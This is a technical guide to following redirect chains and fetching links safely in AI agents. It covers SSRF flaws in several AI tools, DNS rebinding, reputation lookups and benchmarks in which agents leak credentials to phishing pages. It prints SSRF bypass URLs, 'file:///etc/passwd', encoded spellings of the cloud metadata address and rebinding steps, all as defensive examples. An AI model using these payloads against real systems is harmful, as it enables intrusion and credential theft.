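The drawback is that the plugin often doesn't reach the end of the chain. In Ruth's example, even if `short.example` were on the list, the plugin would record the address at `click.example` and stop there. The filter would then check the reputation of a tracking service, and neither the supplier's open redirect nor the fake login page would appear in its results.

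The rules add only 0.01 points to a message's spam score for a chained short link, and SpamAssassin marks a message as spam at 5 points by default. A link that Bitly or TinyURL has disabled for abuse adds 2 points. The plugin's developers evidently regard a chain by itself as very weak evidence of spam, and use expansion mainly to find out where the link leads.

### Chains the plugin failed to follow

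User bug reports from January 2023 show how a list-based expander fails on real links. In one, a `t.co` link from a spam message led to a phishing page. The plugin identified itself as a browser, and `t.co` responded with a refresh tag in the page instead of a Location header. The plugin found no redirect because it read only headers. Its later documentation recommends identifying it to `t.co` as `curl`, a command-line program, to get the correct address for blocked links.

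SpamAssassin's *DecodeShortURLs does not handle some ml-trk redirects* describes links on `ml-trk.com` that redirected to `/rd.html?go=` on the same host, with the final URL encoded after the equals sign. The plugin records a relative address but does not request it, so it stopped one hop before the destination, even though the destination was visible in the query. The published code treats every Location value without a scheme as relative, so it would also mistake `//attacker.example/88` for a page on the shortener's own site.

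SpamAssassin's *DecodeShortURLs fails to follow redirect chains with differing query parameters* describes an `rb.gy` link that redirected to itself with two extra parameters, then to a page stating that the service had disabled the link. The plugin apparently gave up after the first hop. The reporter suspected the loop check ignored query parameters, but later could not reproduce the fault and thought stored results might have caused it.

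The same report describes a simpler failure. The list included `shorturl.at` but not `www.shorturl.at`, where that service first redirects every visitor, so the expansion stopped. The reporter considered adding the missing host, but the plugin would then count the move from `http` to `https` on one site as a chain of short links.

SpamAssassin 4.0.2 added a second plugin for tracking links and other redirectors. According to SpamAssassin's *Redirectors*, the plugin also looks for query parameters that often contain a destination, such as `url`, `redirect` and `target`. The default list has about 25 names, but it doesn't include the `go` from `ml-trk.com` or the `to` in Ruth's chain.

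SpamAssassin used to have separate plugins for shorteners and redirectors, but its developers have merged them, according to the September manual page *DecodeShortURLs* (2026). The combined plugin can follow chains that mix the two kinds of service in any order, and the manual page says there is "no functional difference" between them. SpamAssassin's upgrade notes for version 4.0.3 list a new option to connect to Selenium, a browser-control tool, to catch JavaScript redirects.

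An agent's developer can reuse this plugin's general algorithm but should be wary of its list. A spam filter can work without a link's destination because it has many other clues about the message, but an agent needs the whole chain expanded before it opens the link.

### Running an expander or asking an outside service

A developer can instead send the link to an outside expansion service, which follows the chain on its own machines and returns the destination, often with the hops in between. This saves the developer from maintaining an isolated browser. It also means that the service sees the link and that the requests come from the service rather than the developer.

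| | Own expander | Outside service |
|---|---|---|
| Who receives the original link | The first server in the chain | The service and the first server in the chain |
| Network address in the servers' logs | The developer's or user's | The service's |
| Private machines within reach | Those on the expander's network, unless the developer blocks them | Those on the service's network |
| Who maintains the browser | The developer | The service |
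| Can check the agent's own request at each hop | Yes, if it is part of the agent's tool | No, because it makes separate requests |

The service receives the full URL, the time and usually the identity of the customer who sent it. Some URLs need to be kept secret, because anyone who has a password-reset link or a link to a shared folder may be able to use it. A short link to such a URL exposes just as much, because the service will expand it. Removing the query before sending the link would protect some of this information, but the redirect may not work without the query.

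A service that checked every link in Ruth's inbox would eventually have a list of her suppliers, her bank and perhaps her doctor. The service's terms determine how long it keeps that list and whether it shares it, so a developer should read them before sending it any links from private messages.

An outside service keeps the user's network address out of the attacker's logs, but an attacker who made the code `q7Xk` for Ruth alone can still tie any request for it to her.

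An expander can be a target for server-side request forgery, in which a redirect leads it to internal services. A limit on hops does not prevent this. The redirect resolver in Rspamd, another open-source mail filter, has therefore refused private addresses by default since version 4.1.3.

For an agent that reads private email, a self-hosted expander is usually the better choice, provided that the developer blocks requests to private network addresses. An outside service is better for links that are already public, such as search results, because looking them up reveals little except that somebody is interested in them.

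## Rules to apply at every hop

If a developer turns off automatic redirects, an agent's page-opening tool can pause before each hop, as an expander does, and apply the same rules to every URL in the chain. In 2026, the developers of one AI product had to fix a series of flaws caused by checking only the first URL.

### Why checking the first URL fails

Organizations run Open WebUI on their own servers to chat with language models, and it can fetch web pages and images for the model. Its `validate_url()` function rejects URLs that lead to private addresses, but the program ran it only on the URL the user supplied, then passed that URL to an HTTP client that followed redirects automatically.

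The project's own advisory for this flaw (CVE-2026-45401), reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-RH5X-H6PP-CJJ6* (2026), includes a sample attack. A logged-in user asks the Open WebUI server to fetch a page from `httpbin.org`, a public testing site that redirects visitors to any address in the query. The query contains an address on that same Open WebUI server.

`validate_url()` checked only `httpbin.org`, which has a public address. The client then followed the redirect to `http://localhost:8080/api/config`, and Open WebUI returned its own internal configuration to the user. The advisory lists five places in the code with this fault. The code that loads images into chats was the easiest to reach, because any user could trigger it with an ordinary message containing an image URL.

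The second flaw, CVE-2026-54018, affected servers that load pages in a browser through Playwright, a browser-control tool. The program checked the URL before calling `page.goto(url)`, but the browser then followed redirects on its own. In the project's demonstration, reproduced in OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2743* (2026), an outside server redirects the browser to `http://open-webui:8080/api/version`, an address that exists only on the affected server's internal network. MITRE's *CVE-2026-54018* (2026) rates the severity at 7.7 out of 10.

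The advisory recommended turning off automatic redirects in the ordinary HTTP clients and running `validate_url()` on each Location header. For the browser, it recommended an interceptor, code that Playwright runs before each request and that can cancel it.

The developers first responded in version 0.9.5 by refusing all redirects unless an administrator turned them back on, according to the release notes copied in gitea.alexlebens.dev's *chore(deps)* (2026). This setting is safe, but it also breaks short links and routine moves from `http` to `https`, so some administrators had a good reason to change it. Those who did lost the protection, because the program didn't check where redirects led until version 0.11.1 (Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-88001*, 2026).

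The repairs took several versions:

| Version | What the developers fixed | What an attacker could still use |
|---|---|---|
| 0.9.5 | Five places where ordinary HTTP clients followed redirects | A sixth place, the browser, and any server with redirects turned back on |
| 0.9.6 | The sixth place, and page loads in the browser | Requests from scripts inside a page, a second address lookup by the browser, and any server with redirects turned back on |
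| 0.11.0 | All requests from the browser | A second address lookup by the browser, and any server with redirects turned back on |
| 0.11.1 | The browser's second lookup, and servers with redirects turned back on | None of the routes above |

The sixth place was the code that downloads a user's profile picture from a login service, according to the advisory in Corgea's *Open WebUI*. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3653* (2026) attributes the gap in version 0.9.6 to an interceptor that checked only the request for the page itself. A page on a public host could pass the check, then use a script to make the browser request an internal address and display the response, which Open WebUI returned to the user.

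Developers can avoid much of this by writing the rules once and checking every request against them, whether it comes from a link, a redirect, an image or a script.

### The rules, with examples

In these examples, the allowlist contains only `docs.example.com` and its subdomains, except in the last row, where the developer has also allowed the two hosts shown.

| Rule | Passes | Fails |
|---|---|---|
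| The scheme is `http` or `https` | `https://docs.example.com/start` | `file:///etc/passwd` |
| The URL names one host unambiguously | `https://docs.example.com:8443/` | `https://docs.example.com:pass@localhost:8080/` |
| The lists permit the host | `https://eu.docs.example.com/` | `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` |
| All the host's network addresses are public | A host at `93.184.216.34` | A host at `192.168.0.10` |
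| The redirect does not go from HTTPS to HTTP | `http://docs.example.com/` to `https://docs.example.com/` | `https://docs.example.com/` to `http://docs.example.com/` |
| Credentials stay with the host they belong to | `https://api.example.com/v1` to `https://api.example.com/v2`, with the access key | `https://api.example.com/v1` to `https://files.example.net/`, with the access key |

The agent should check the scheme first because it determines what the rest of the URL means. For example, `file:///etc/passwd` points to a file on the machine that runs the tool. Developers should permit only the two web schemes, `http` and `https`, because a list of dangerous schemes might omit one.

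### Finding the host

browser-use is an open-source library that lets a language model operate a browser. Developers can give it a list called `allowed_domains`. In 2025, researchers at ARIMLABS.AI found a way around that list, which GitLab's *CVE-2025-47241* (2025) catalogues. OSV's *GHSA-x39x-9qw5-ghrf* (2025) rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10 and gives an example that passes when the list contains only `example.com`:

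`https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080`

1. The library took the part of the URL between the two slashes and the path, which is `example.com:pass@localhost:8080`.
2. To remove the port number, it cut this text at the first colon and kept `example.com`.
3. It found `example.com` on the list and approved the URL.
4. The browser read `example.com` as a user name and `pass` as a password, and connected to `localhost`.

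The list was fine, but the library compared it with the wrong piece of text, even though the Python parser it had already called provides the correct host as a separate value. Version 0.1.45 fixed the flaw.

A standard parser does not help if the HTTP client reads the URL differently. Corgea's *Open WebUI has a Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF) bypass in `validate_url`* reproduces an advisory about this URL:

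`http://127.0.0.1:6666\@1.1.1.1`

The parser in `validate_url()` treated everything before the at-sign as a user name and reported the host as `1.1.1.1`, a public address. The client treated the backslash as the start of the path, so it connected to `127.0.0.1`, the server itself. Open WebUI now rejects URLs that contain backslashes, tabs or line breaks.

A more general solution is to parse the URL once and build the request from the parsed parts, so that the check and the client always use the same interpretation of it. Developers can also refuse any URL that contains a user name, since ordinary web links almost never need one.

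### Matching the host against a list

A host name consists of labels separated by dots, and the owner of a domain controls every name that ends with a dot followed by that domain. A list entry should therefore match the exact host or a name that ends with a dot and the entry:

```
host == entry  or  host ends with "." + entry
```

Open WebUI's code left out the dot and, in its main fetching code, compared the entry with the end of the whole URL. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3603* (2026) lists the results:

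| List entry | URL or host | What the code did | What it should have done |
|---|---|---|---|
| Block `internal.example.com` | `https://internal.example.com/x` | Allowed it | Refuse |
| Allow `company.com` | `https://api.company.com/status` | Refused it | Allow |
| Allow `company.com` | `https://attacker.example/path/company.com` | Allowed it | Refuse |
| `corp.com` | `evilcorp.com` | Matched | Not match |
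| `10.0.0.1` | `110.0.0.1` | Matched | Not match |

The blocklist stopped only URLs with no path. Version 0.10.0 introduced the comparison shown above and applies it to the parsed host. Numeric addresses have no subdomains, so that version requires them to match exactly.

Developers still need to know how a given tool matches list entries to hosts. In the fetch tool of Docker Agent, Docker's program for running AI agents, `example.com` covers the domain and its subdomains, while `.example.com` covers only the subdomains. Docker's *Fetch Tool* also explains that the tool removes a final dot from the host, because `example.com.` and `example.com` lead to the same place and a blocklist could otherwise miss one of them.

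An allowlist suits an agent with a narrow job. If Ruth's agent only had to read this supplier's invoices, its list could contain just `docs.example.com`. The open redirect on that host would not help the attacker, because the tool would refuse the next hop. But the tool would also refuse the link to the genuine invoice, because it starts at `short.example`. The developer could add the shortener to the list, which is reasonable only if the tool also checks every hop after it.

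An agent that researches arbitrary topics cannot use an allowlist, so it needs a blocklist. A blocklist stops only the hosts that someone thought to include.

### Refusing private addresses

Neither kind of list reliably protects the private network, because anyone who owns a domain can point it at any numeric address. The owner of `attacker.example` could point it at `192.168.0.10`, for example. The tool therefore has to look up the host in the domain name system (DNS), which translates names into addresses, and check the resulting addresses.

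| Addresses | What they are for |
|---|---|
| `127.0.0.0/8` and `::1` | Loopback: the machine that sends the request |
| `10.0.0.0/8`, `172.16.0.0/12` and `192.168.0.0/16` | Private networks in homes and companies |
| `169.254.0.0/16` and `fe80::/10` | Link-local: machines on the same stretch of network, and most cloud metadata services |
| `100.64.0.0/10` | Networks inside internet providers |
| `0.0.0.0` and `::` | "Unspecified", which can lead back to the machine itself |

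The number after the slash shows how many bits at the start of the address are fixed. For example, `10.0.0.0/8` covers every address that begins with 10. The addresses with colons are in IPv6, the newer and longer format.

The cloud metadata address, `169.254.169.254`, needs particular attention. A program on a rented cloud server can request information about that server from this address, and on some configurations the response includes temporary credentials for the customer's cloud account. Older versions of the metadata service return these credentials in response to a plain GET request, which is what a page-opening tool sends.

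Open WebUI's checks for private addresses failed in three ways. Its early code used a library to check whether an IPv6 address was private, with an option that the library didn't support for IPv6. The library returned an error, which Python treated as false, so every IPv6 address passed. Corgea's *Open WebUI has a full SSRF Vulnerability in the RAG Web Search* credits a September 2024 report with first identifying this flaw.

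From version 0.9.0, the program used Python's built-in test of whether an address is "globally routable". According to NVD's *CVE-2026-70485* (2026), that test missed internal addresses wrapped in a special IPv6 form. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-87999* (2026) records that it also passed `168.63.129.16`, which Microsoft's Azure cloud uses for internal communication with customers' servers. This address comes from ordinary public address space, so Python classified it correctly. But as SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-87999* points out, the test reflects how a registry has classified an address, not what a particular server can reach. Developers therefore need to add their own cloud provider's special addresses to the standard ranges.

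### One address, several spellings

An IPv4 address is a single 32-bit number, and the familiar four-part form is only one way to write it. The metadata address works out as:

169 × 256³ + 254 × 256² + 169 × 256 + 254 = 2,852,039,166

Many programs accept that number in place of the usual form, along with several others:

| Spelling of `169.254.169.254` | Form |
|---|---|
| `2852039166` | One decimal number |
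| `0xa9.0xfe.0xa9.0xfe` | Hexadecimal, base 16 |
| `0251.0376.0251.0376` | Octal, base 8 |
| `::ffff:169.254.169.254` | IPv4 address inside an IPv6 address |
| `64:ff9b::a9fe:a9fe` | The form for NAT64, a gateway that connects IPv6 networks to IPv4 addresses |

A blocklist that compares text would catch the usual spelling of an address but miss most of the others. Docker warns that its lists miss decimal, hexadecimal and octal forms, though they recognize the first of the two IPv6 forms. The fix is to convert the host to its numeric value, extract any IPv4 address embedded in an IPv6 one, and only then compare the result with the forbidden ranges.

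### Refusing a drop from HTTPS to HTTP

HTTPS encrypts the connection and uses a certificate to confirm that the server controls the host name, but HTTP does neither. If a chain moves from HTTPS to HTTP, anyone between the agent and the next server, such as the operator of a public Wi-Fi network, can read the request and replace the response. They could insert a prompt injection into the page or redirect the agent to another host.

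The AI SDK, Vercel's toolkit for building AI applications, refuses a redirect from HTTPS to HTTP before it contacts the HTTP address. According to AI SDK's *Secure URL Fetching*, this applies to server-side downloads even if the developer has marked the destination as trusted. The toolkit still accepts HTTP links and redirects from HTTP to HTTPS, so most old links should work.

### Removing credentials when the host changes

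A tool may attach credentials to a request, typically an access key in the Authorization header. If the server redirects the tool to another host and the tool sends the header again, the new host's operator receives the key. The redirect may be legitimate, as when a service stores its files on another company's servers, so the tool can follow it but should not send the key.

Developers who write their own code to follow redirects carefully can still expose credentials to another host. AutoGPT, a platform for building agents, turned off automatic redirects and requested each new address itself. Many HTTP libraries remove credentials when they follow a redirect to another host, but AutoGPT's code did not. NVD's *CVE-2025-31491* describes a hypothetical open redirect on GitHub's servers. An agent that visited it with a user's GitHub key would have sent the key to whatever site the redirect named.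 Version 0.6.1 fixed the flaw.

According to Docker's documentation, Go's standard library removes three sensitive headers on a redirect to another domain: Authorization, Cookie and WWW-Authenticate. That list would miss the keys that many services accept in other headers, so Docker's tool removes every header the operator added. The AI SDK goes slightly further. It compares origins (scheme, host and port) and, when the origin changes, drops all the caller's headers except the one that identifies the software.

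The AI SDK also never restores credentials later in the chain. This matters if `api.example.com` redirects to `attacker.example`, which redirects back to `api.example.com`. If the SDK restored them, the attacker could choose which page on the original service the agent opened with the user's authority.

If a model has picked a URL from an email, the tool should attach a key even to the first request only when the URL matches a host that the developer configured for that key. The AI SDK's `fetchUntrustedUrl` function works this way, but an older function in the same toolkit still sends authentication headers with the first request.

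### DNS rebinding

All these rules can approve a URL correctly and the request can still reach a private address. In a DNS rebinding attack, the attacker changes the address behind a host name between the check and the connection. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-87996* sets out the sequence for Open WebUI:

1. The attacker registers a domain and runs the DNS server that answers questions about `rebind.attacker.example`. Each answer comes with an instruction to remember it for only a second or less.
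2. The attacker submits a URL on that host.
3. The program looks up the host and receives `93.184.216.34`, a public address, so the URL passes.
4. The HTTP client or browser looks up the host again, because the first answer has expired or because it never saw that answer.
5. The attacker's server now answers `169.254.169.254`.
6. The client connects to the metadata service and returns the response.

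This attack works without a redirect or any change to the URL. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3647* (2026) describes the failed check as "an opinion about a past lookup". It notes that the attacker has to win a race between the two lookups and can influence the timing but not fully control it. The attack is therefore less reliable than a plain redirect, though an attacker can usually try again.

The tool should look up the host once, check every address returned, and connect only to one of those addresses, a practice developers call pinning. It should refuse the host if any address is private, since the client may try them in turn. The client still has to use the host name in the Host header and when it checks the server's certificate, or most HTTPS sites will not work.

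Pinning is harder with a browser because it does its own lookups. Open WebUI checked the address in Python, but then let the browser look up the name again. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-87996* (2026) dates this flaw from version 0.9.6 until 0.11.1. According to SecureLayer7, the interceptor in the repaired version no longer lets the browser make these requests. Instead, Open WebUI fetches each file through its own protected client and gives the browser the contents.

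Where the address check runs also matters. In Open WebUI, one version of the check ran in the DNS resolver. A redirect to `http://169.254.169.254/` contains a numeric address and needs no lookup, so the check never ran. Miggo's *CVE-2026-88001* reports that the developers moved the check to the component that opens connections, which handles both names and numeric addresses.

With pinning, the full check on each URL looks like this:

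```
check(url, previous):
    if url contains a backslash, tab or line break:  refuse
    parse url once
    if the scheme is not http or https:              refuse
    if url contains a user name:                     refuse
    if the lists do not permit the host:             refuse
    if previous is https and url is http:            refuse

    addresses = look up the host,
                or read the numeric address in url
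    if there are none, or any is forbidden:          refuse

    if the origin differs from that of previous:
        remove credentials for the rest of the chain
    connect to one of addresses, using the host's name
```

The first URL has no `previous`, so the tool skips the HTTPS comparison and uses the developer's configuration to determine whether to attach credentials. A lookup can reach a DNS server that the attacker runs, so the tool first finishes the checks that need no network request, such as the HTTPS rule.

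### Two documented designs

The AI SDK and Docker Agent's fetch tool both check redirects hop by hop. They differ most in what they do about DNS.

| | AI SDK | Docker Agent's fetch tool |
|---|---|---|
| Host lists | Trusted origins that skip certain checks, but no general list | An allowlist or a blocklist, if the developer sets one |
| Redirects | Checks every hop | Checks every hop against the list |
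| Private numeric address in the URL | Refuses by default | Refuses by default |
| Host name that leads to a private address | Refuses only with an optional component | Refuses by default when it connects |
| HTTPS to HTTP | Refuses for server-side downloads | Documents no such rule |
| Credentials when the host changes | Removes all the caller's headers except User-Agent | Removes all headers the operator added |

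By default, the AI SDK checks the text of a URL, including any numeric address, but does not look up host names. It therefore blocks a redirect to `http://10.0.0.5/` but allows one to a host name that resolves to the same address. Developers can close this gap by installing the `guarded-fetch` package, which checks every address in the DNS answer and connects only to the addresses it has checked. The package requires Node.js and does not support several other JavaScript runtimes.

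The developer also has to connect `guarded-fetch` in the right places. The AI SDK's automatic checks cover URLs that come back from outside services, such as the address of a generated image. A page-opening tool that the developer writes needs its own configuration, and so do the toolkit's general file downloads. If the application passes a URL straight to a model provider, the provider's servers fetch it without the developer's checks. Open WebUI had the same difficulty with its six places, although here the documentation warns about it.

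Docker's tool has safer defaults. It accepts only GET requests and refuses private addresses at the moment it connects, which also defeats DNS rebinding. A developer who needs an internal service can set `allow_private_ips` to true. Docker recommends combining that setting with an allowlist, because the setting alone allows requests to every private address the machine can reach.

The exception is for Docker Desktop, Docker's application for personal computers. When it is running, the tool may send requests for hosts under `docker.com` and `docker.io` through Docker Desktop's proxy. The proxy makes the connection, so the tool cannot check the final address. The tool first looks up the host and normally uses the proxy only if all the addresses it gets back are public. If the lookup takes more than two seconds, however, it can use the proxy without an answer. The risk seems small because Docker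 owns those domains, and requests for every other host stay on the protected path.

For an agent that only reads pages, Docker's defaults are the better starting point because they protect against rebinding without any changes. The AI SDK can provide similar protection and has the useful HTTPS rule, but only a developer who has read the documentation is likely to turn all of it on.

### Controls on the network itself

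Application code can only check the requests that pass through it. Egress controls are rules on outbound traffic that a firewall, outbound proxy or container settings enforce from outside the application. A rule might let the machine running the agent's browser connect to the public internet but not to `10.0.0.0/8` or `169.254.169.254`.

Such a firewall rule applies to every request, whichever library made it. It would have stopped the attacks on internal addresses through Open WebUI's forgotten profile-picture code and through scripts in the browser. It would also have covered browser traffic that never reached the interceptor, namely requests from service workers (background scripts) and WebSockets (long-lived connections). Different spellings of an address and repeated DNS lookups don't get around the rule, because a firewall checks the numeric address of the actual connection. The OSV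 entry on the browser scripts states that a server whose browser had no route to internal services lost nothing to that flaw.

The AI SDK's documentation calls egress controls the broadest protection and advises blocking private, loopback, link-local and metadata addresses over both IPv4 and IPv6. Loopback needs separate attention because traffic from a machine to itself never crosses an external firewall. A developer can run the browser in its own container, where `localhost` means only that container. If traffic leaves through a proxy, the proxy has to apply the address rules because it looks up the destination and connects to it. A web application firewall that filters incoming visits does not control these outgoing requests.

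Egress controls are hard to apply to an agent like Ruth's, which works in the browser on her office computer. She may need that browser for the company's internal pages, so her employer cannot simply cut it off from the private network. Giving the agent a separate browser on an isolated machine would solve this, but it would require signing in again to each account the agent needs.

A firewall also has much less information about each request than the application does. It can block `192.168.0.10`, but it often cannot distinguish a permitted site from a forbidden one by address, because many unrelated websites share public addresses. It normally cannot read HTTPS traffic, so it would not detect an access key sent to the wrong host. The application should therefore enforce the host lists and the credential rule, and both the application and the firewall should enforce the address rule.

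## Judging whether a link or its chain is malicious

The fake login page in Ruth's chain could pass almost every rule in the previous section. Its host, `docs.example.com.attacker.example`, can have a public address and a valid certificate, so only an allowlist would reliably exclude it. An agent that has to visit unfamiliar sites needs to estimate whether a link is malicious. It can use the text of the URL, earlier reports about the address, or the redirect chain as a whole.

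### The text of the URL

A URL's text is the easiest evidence to check because software can read it without contacting a server. *SiNMULI* (2026), which proposes a detector for malicious URLs, lists the usual warning signs: a numeric address instead of a host name, a link shortener, an unusual top-level domain (the last part of the host, such as `.com`), an at-sign, and a long, deeply nested path. Legitimate links can have any of these features, and an attacker can avoid them all by registering a plain-looking domain.

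Attackers can encode even the letters of a redirect link's destination. In an example from *Comprehensive List of User Deception Techniques in Emails*, the destination starts with `%68%74` instead of `ht`. Software should decode the query and examine any URL it finds there.

Simple text classifiers do badly on current scams. *ReDence* (Kaur, Horáček and colleagues, 2026) tested URLNet, a neural network that judges a URL by its characters and words, on 1,551 scam sites and 1,500 legitimate ones. It caught 19% of the scams, and only 35% of its alarms were correct, compared with about 51% if it had flagged sites at random. Most of the scams were fake shops, loans and job offers, which have less need to imitate a known address than a fake bank does.

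Language models may judge URLs poorly, even though they are trained on far more text about the web than small classifiers are. *MalURLBench* (Kong, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 models on samples from a set of 61,845 disguised URLs built from real malicious sites. Each test put a URL into a short message from one of ten everyday scenarios, such as tracking a parcel or checking the weather, and the instructions told the model to watch for attacks. Depending on the model, between 32.9% and 99.9% of the attacks succeeded, meaning the model accepted the URL.

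The disguises were of two kinds, shown here with `attacker.example` in place of the malicious site:

| Disguise | Example | Average success |
|---|---|---|
| A reassuring phrase | `attacker.example/?this-is-a-popular-food-delivery-service` | 71.5% |
| A well-known site's name | `www.google.com.www.attacker.example` | 60.9% |

The lowest figure, 32.9%, is for GPT-3.5 Turbo, which had accepted about 14% of the URLs on average before the researchers rewrote some of the disguises to make them more effective. They did this when a model accepted 10% or fewer of the URLs in a scenario. The models, which include GPT-4o and Llama 2, are also old, and none is from 2026.

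In the benchmark, the attacker could change only the subdomain, path and parameters, so the malicious domain was visible in every URL. A short link such as `https://short.example/q7Xk` hides the destination domain, so the results are relevant to short links only after expansion, when the software can examine the URL at each hop.

Kong and colleagues also built a filter, URLGuard, by training a small Llama 2 model on 280 labeled URLs, half of them malicious. The malicious examples all imitated the shopping scenario, and the researchers tested the filter on the other nine scenarios. The original model accepted about 98% of the malicious URLs, and URLGuard accepted about 17%. URLGuard accepted far more of them in the music (61%) and weather (70%) scenarios than in the rest. The researchers report results only for malicious URLs, so it is unclear how many legitimate links URLGuard would refuse.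 The test URLs also used the same kinds of disguise as the training examples.

### Newer models and known addresses

Models from 2026 still send passwords to the wrong host. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi et al., 2026) tested seven models, including Claude Opus 4.8, Claude Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.6 Luna, with access to invented accounts. The models encountered fake login pages with misspelled domains, wrong top-level domains, look-alike letters, numeric addresses or misleading subdomains. Every model gave account details to some of these pages, both when the user asked it to log in and when its only task was to sort an inbox.

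When the user's request stressed caution, some models left almost all the legitimate tasks unfinished. Giving the models the services' real domains and telling them to check against those worked better. Most models then leaked less and completed more of the genuine logins that users had asked for. The services were fictional, so the models could not have learned the correct domains in training.

This suggests an agent should compare a host with a known address whenever it can, instead of judging whether the host looks suspicious. Ruth's agent could take the supplier's domain from her address book or from an invoice she has already paid. Ordinary code should make the comparison, since matching two host names does not require a language model.

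An agent that avoids a fake page may still fail to complete the user's task. Some of the phishing emails in CredLeakBench concerned a real task, such as a bill the user needed to pay, and the correct address was available elsewhere. The best model reached the real site without leaking anything in only 27.7% of these cases.

Models do much better when asked directly whether a site is a scam. For *ScamWorld*, Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026) rebuilt 363 reported scam sites and 53 legitimate ones, then tested agents based on six recent models. They first gave each agent an ordinary task, such as buying a product. In a separate test, they asked it to look around the same site and decide whether the site was legitimate.

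Depending on the model, agents took a harmful final step, such as paying or entering credentials, on 11% to 35% of the scam sites. When asked directly, they identified 88% to 100% of the sites as scams. DeepSeek V4.1 Flash had the largest gap, identifying 98% when asked but taking the harmful step on 35% during ordinary tasks. Some agents noticed a problem but continued because they treated the user's request as permission.

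The agents in this test could read the pages, so they had more evidence than the URL alone. The researchers also added a visible warning sign to about half of the scam sites, which may have made them easier to recognize than the originals. Even so, the gap is large enough that developers should ask about the site's legitimacy in a separate step rather than expect the agent to raise it while shopping.

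### Looking up an address's reputation

A reputation service keeps a list of addresses that people or automated scanners have identified as malicious. Google Safe Browsing, which provides the warnings in Chrome, Safari and Firefox, lets software check a URL without revealing it in full. Google's *URLs and Hashing* sets out the procedure:

1. The client puts the URL into a standard form. It removes the fragment, decodes character codes, and converts the different spellings of a numeric address into one.
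2. It combines the host and its parent domains with the path and its parent folders, which gives up to 30 combinations.
3. It applies SHA-256, a hash function with a 32-byte output, to each combination.
4. It sends Google only the first four bytes of each hash.
5. Google returns the full hashes of any known threats that start with those bytes, and the client compares them with its own.

For the fake login page in Ruth's chain, the client would check eight combinations:

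```
docs.example.com.attacker.example/login
docs.example.com.attacker.example/
example.com.attacker.example/login
example.com.attacker.example/
com.attacker.example/login
com.attacker.example/
attacker.example/login
attacker.example/
```

If Google has listed `attacker.example/`, the last combination matches no matter which subdomain or page the attacker uses. Google can also list a single page. An entry for `short.example/q7Xk` would block Ruth's link without blocking the shortener's other links.

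A four-byte prefix has about 4.3 billion possible values, and many URLs share each one, so a single prefix does not identify the page. Google also offers a simpler method in which the client sends the whole URL. Google's *Overview* of Safe Browsing warns that this method gives no confidentiality, so it is a poor choice for links from private email. Safe Browsing is free for non-commercial use. Web Risk, Google's equivalent for businesses, follows the same steps, according to Google Cloud's *Hashing URLs*.

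An agent's software should look up each URL in the chain before requesting it. Somebody may have reported the short link while the final page is too new to be on any list, or the attacker may have put a new short link in front of a page that has been listed for days. Looking up an open redirect does not check its destination, because Safe Browsing treats the URL in the query string as ordinary text. The software has to extract that URL and look it up separately, or look it up once the server returns it in a Location header.

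### New addresses that the lists miss

Like any blocklist, a reputation list misses addresses that nobody has reported yet. Kaur and colleagues measured how much this matters in October 2026. Their system, ReDence, examined sites on domains with newly issued security certificates and found 4,042 that the researchers confirmed as scams. They then visited each site repeatedly for a week with four protection products:

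| Product | Flagged at discovery | Flagged within seven days | Fake logins flagged at discovery | Other scams flagged at discovery |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Google Safe Browsing | 16.3% | 33.0% | 44.1% | 7.9% |
| Microsoft SmartScreen | 15.2% | 31.3% | 41.6% | 7.3% |
| Malwarebytes Browser Guard | 16.0% | 38.4% | 36.8% | 9.7% |
| Norton Safe Web | 20.1% | 46.1% | 49.9% | 11.2% |

Together, the four products flagged 27.5% of the sites at discovery. The seven-day figures probably overstate how well the products perform, because the researchers reported every site to them immediately. But the sample consists of new sites, which are the hardest for any list to cover, so Safe Browsing could catch a larger share of the malicious links in an ordinary inbox.

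Among the scam sites that Safe Browsing eventually flagged, the median delay was about 30 hours for sites that impersonated banks and 96 hours for fake shops. An agent that opens an email within minutes of its arrival will often reach a scam site before Safe Browsing flags it.

Google has tried to reduce the delay. Browsers used to download a list of threats periodically and allow everything else. With the current version of Safe Browsing, a client can instead download a list of sites that are probably harmless and ask Google about any other address in real time. This is better for an agent, but it still catches only threats Google has identified.

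Attackers also try to keep scanners from seeing their pages. *An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild* (2026) examined phishing kits, ready-made packages for building fake sites, and found lists of blocked network addresses in 600 of them. The blocked addresses included Google's. A link made for one recipient is even harder to catch because nobody else may ever open and report it.

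Phishing blocklists can add the same domain at very different times. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (2025) compared several with the list kept by the APWG, an industry group that collects phishing reports. Among domains that each list shared with the APWG's, Phishing.Database added them a median of 64 days after the APWG did, and Phishunt.io more than 900 days after. A developer can improve coverage by checking more than one list, but should treat an address that is on none of them as unknown, not safe.

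### The shape of the chain

Attackers can easily create new short links and landing pages, but they often reuse the servers in between. Two older studies tried to detect malicious links from this reuse, without relying on the final page's content.

*WARNINGBIRD* (Lee and Kim, 2012) describes a spam operation on Twitter that used 6,585 accounts and short links, all of which led through the same site, `blackraybansunglasses.com`. That site sent ordinary browsers to spam pages and automated visitors to Google, so a scanner that checked only the final page would have missed the spam.

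Their system collected 10,000 tweets at a time and followed the redirects in each one. It then identified each chain's "entry point", the URL in the chain that was most common across the batch, and calculated 12 features. Some described the chains, including their length and the number of different first links and landing pages connected to the entry point. Others described the tweets and the accounts that posted them. Chain length was the most useful feature.

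The researchers trained the system on 60 days of tweets from 2011 and tested it on the following month. They reported 93.1% accuracy, with 3.7% false positives and 3.2% false negatives. These figures add up to 100%, so the error rates are shares of all URLs tested. Of the 96,309 entry points, 4,421 were malicious. The system therefore missed about 70% of the malicious ones, and about 27% of those it flagged were malicious.

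Some of the apparent false alarms were probably malicious URLs, because the researchers counted a URL as malicious only if Twitter had suspended the accounts that posted it. They later checked 14,905 accounts that the system had flagged and estimated that about 86% were suspicious.

*Shady Paths* (Stringhini, Kruegel and Vigna, 2013) used redirect chains recorded in people's browsers instead of by a crawler. An antivirus company provided 388,098 chains from its customers in 145 countries. The paper's system, SpiderWeb, combined all the chains that led to the same page or similar pages into a graph. It used 28 features, including the variety of visitors' browsers and countries, whether most chains passed through one shared page, and whether any step stayed on the same domain.

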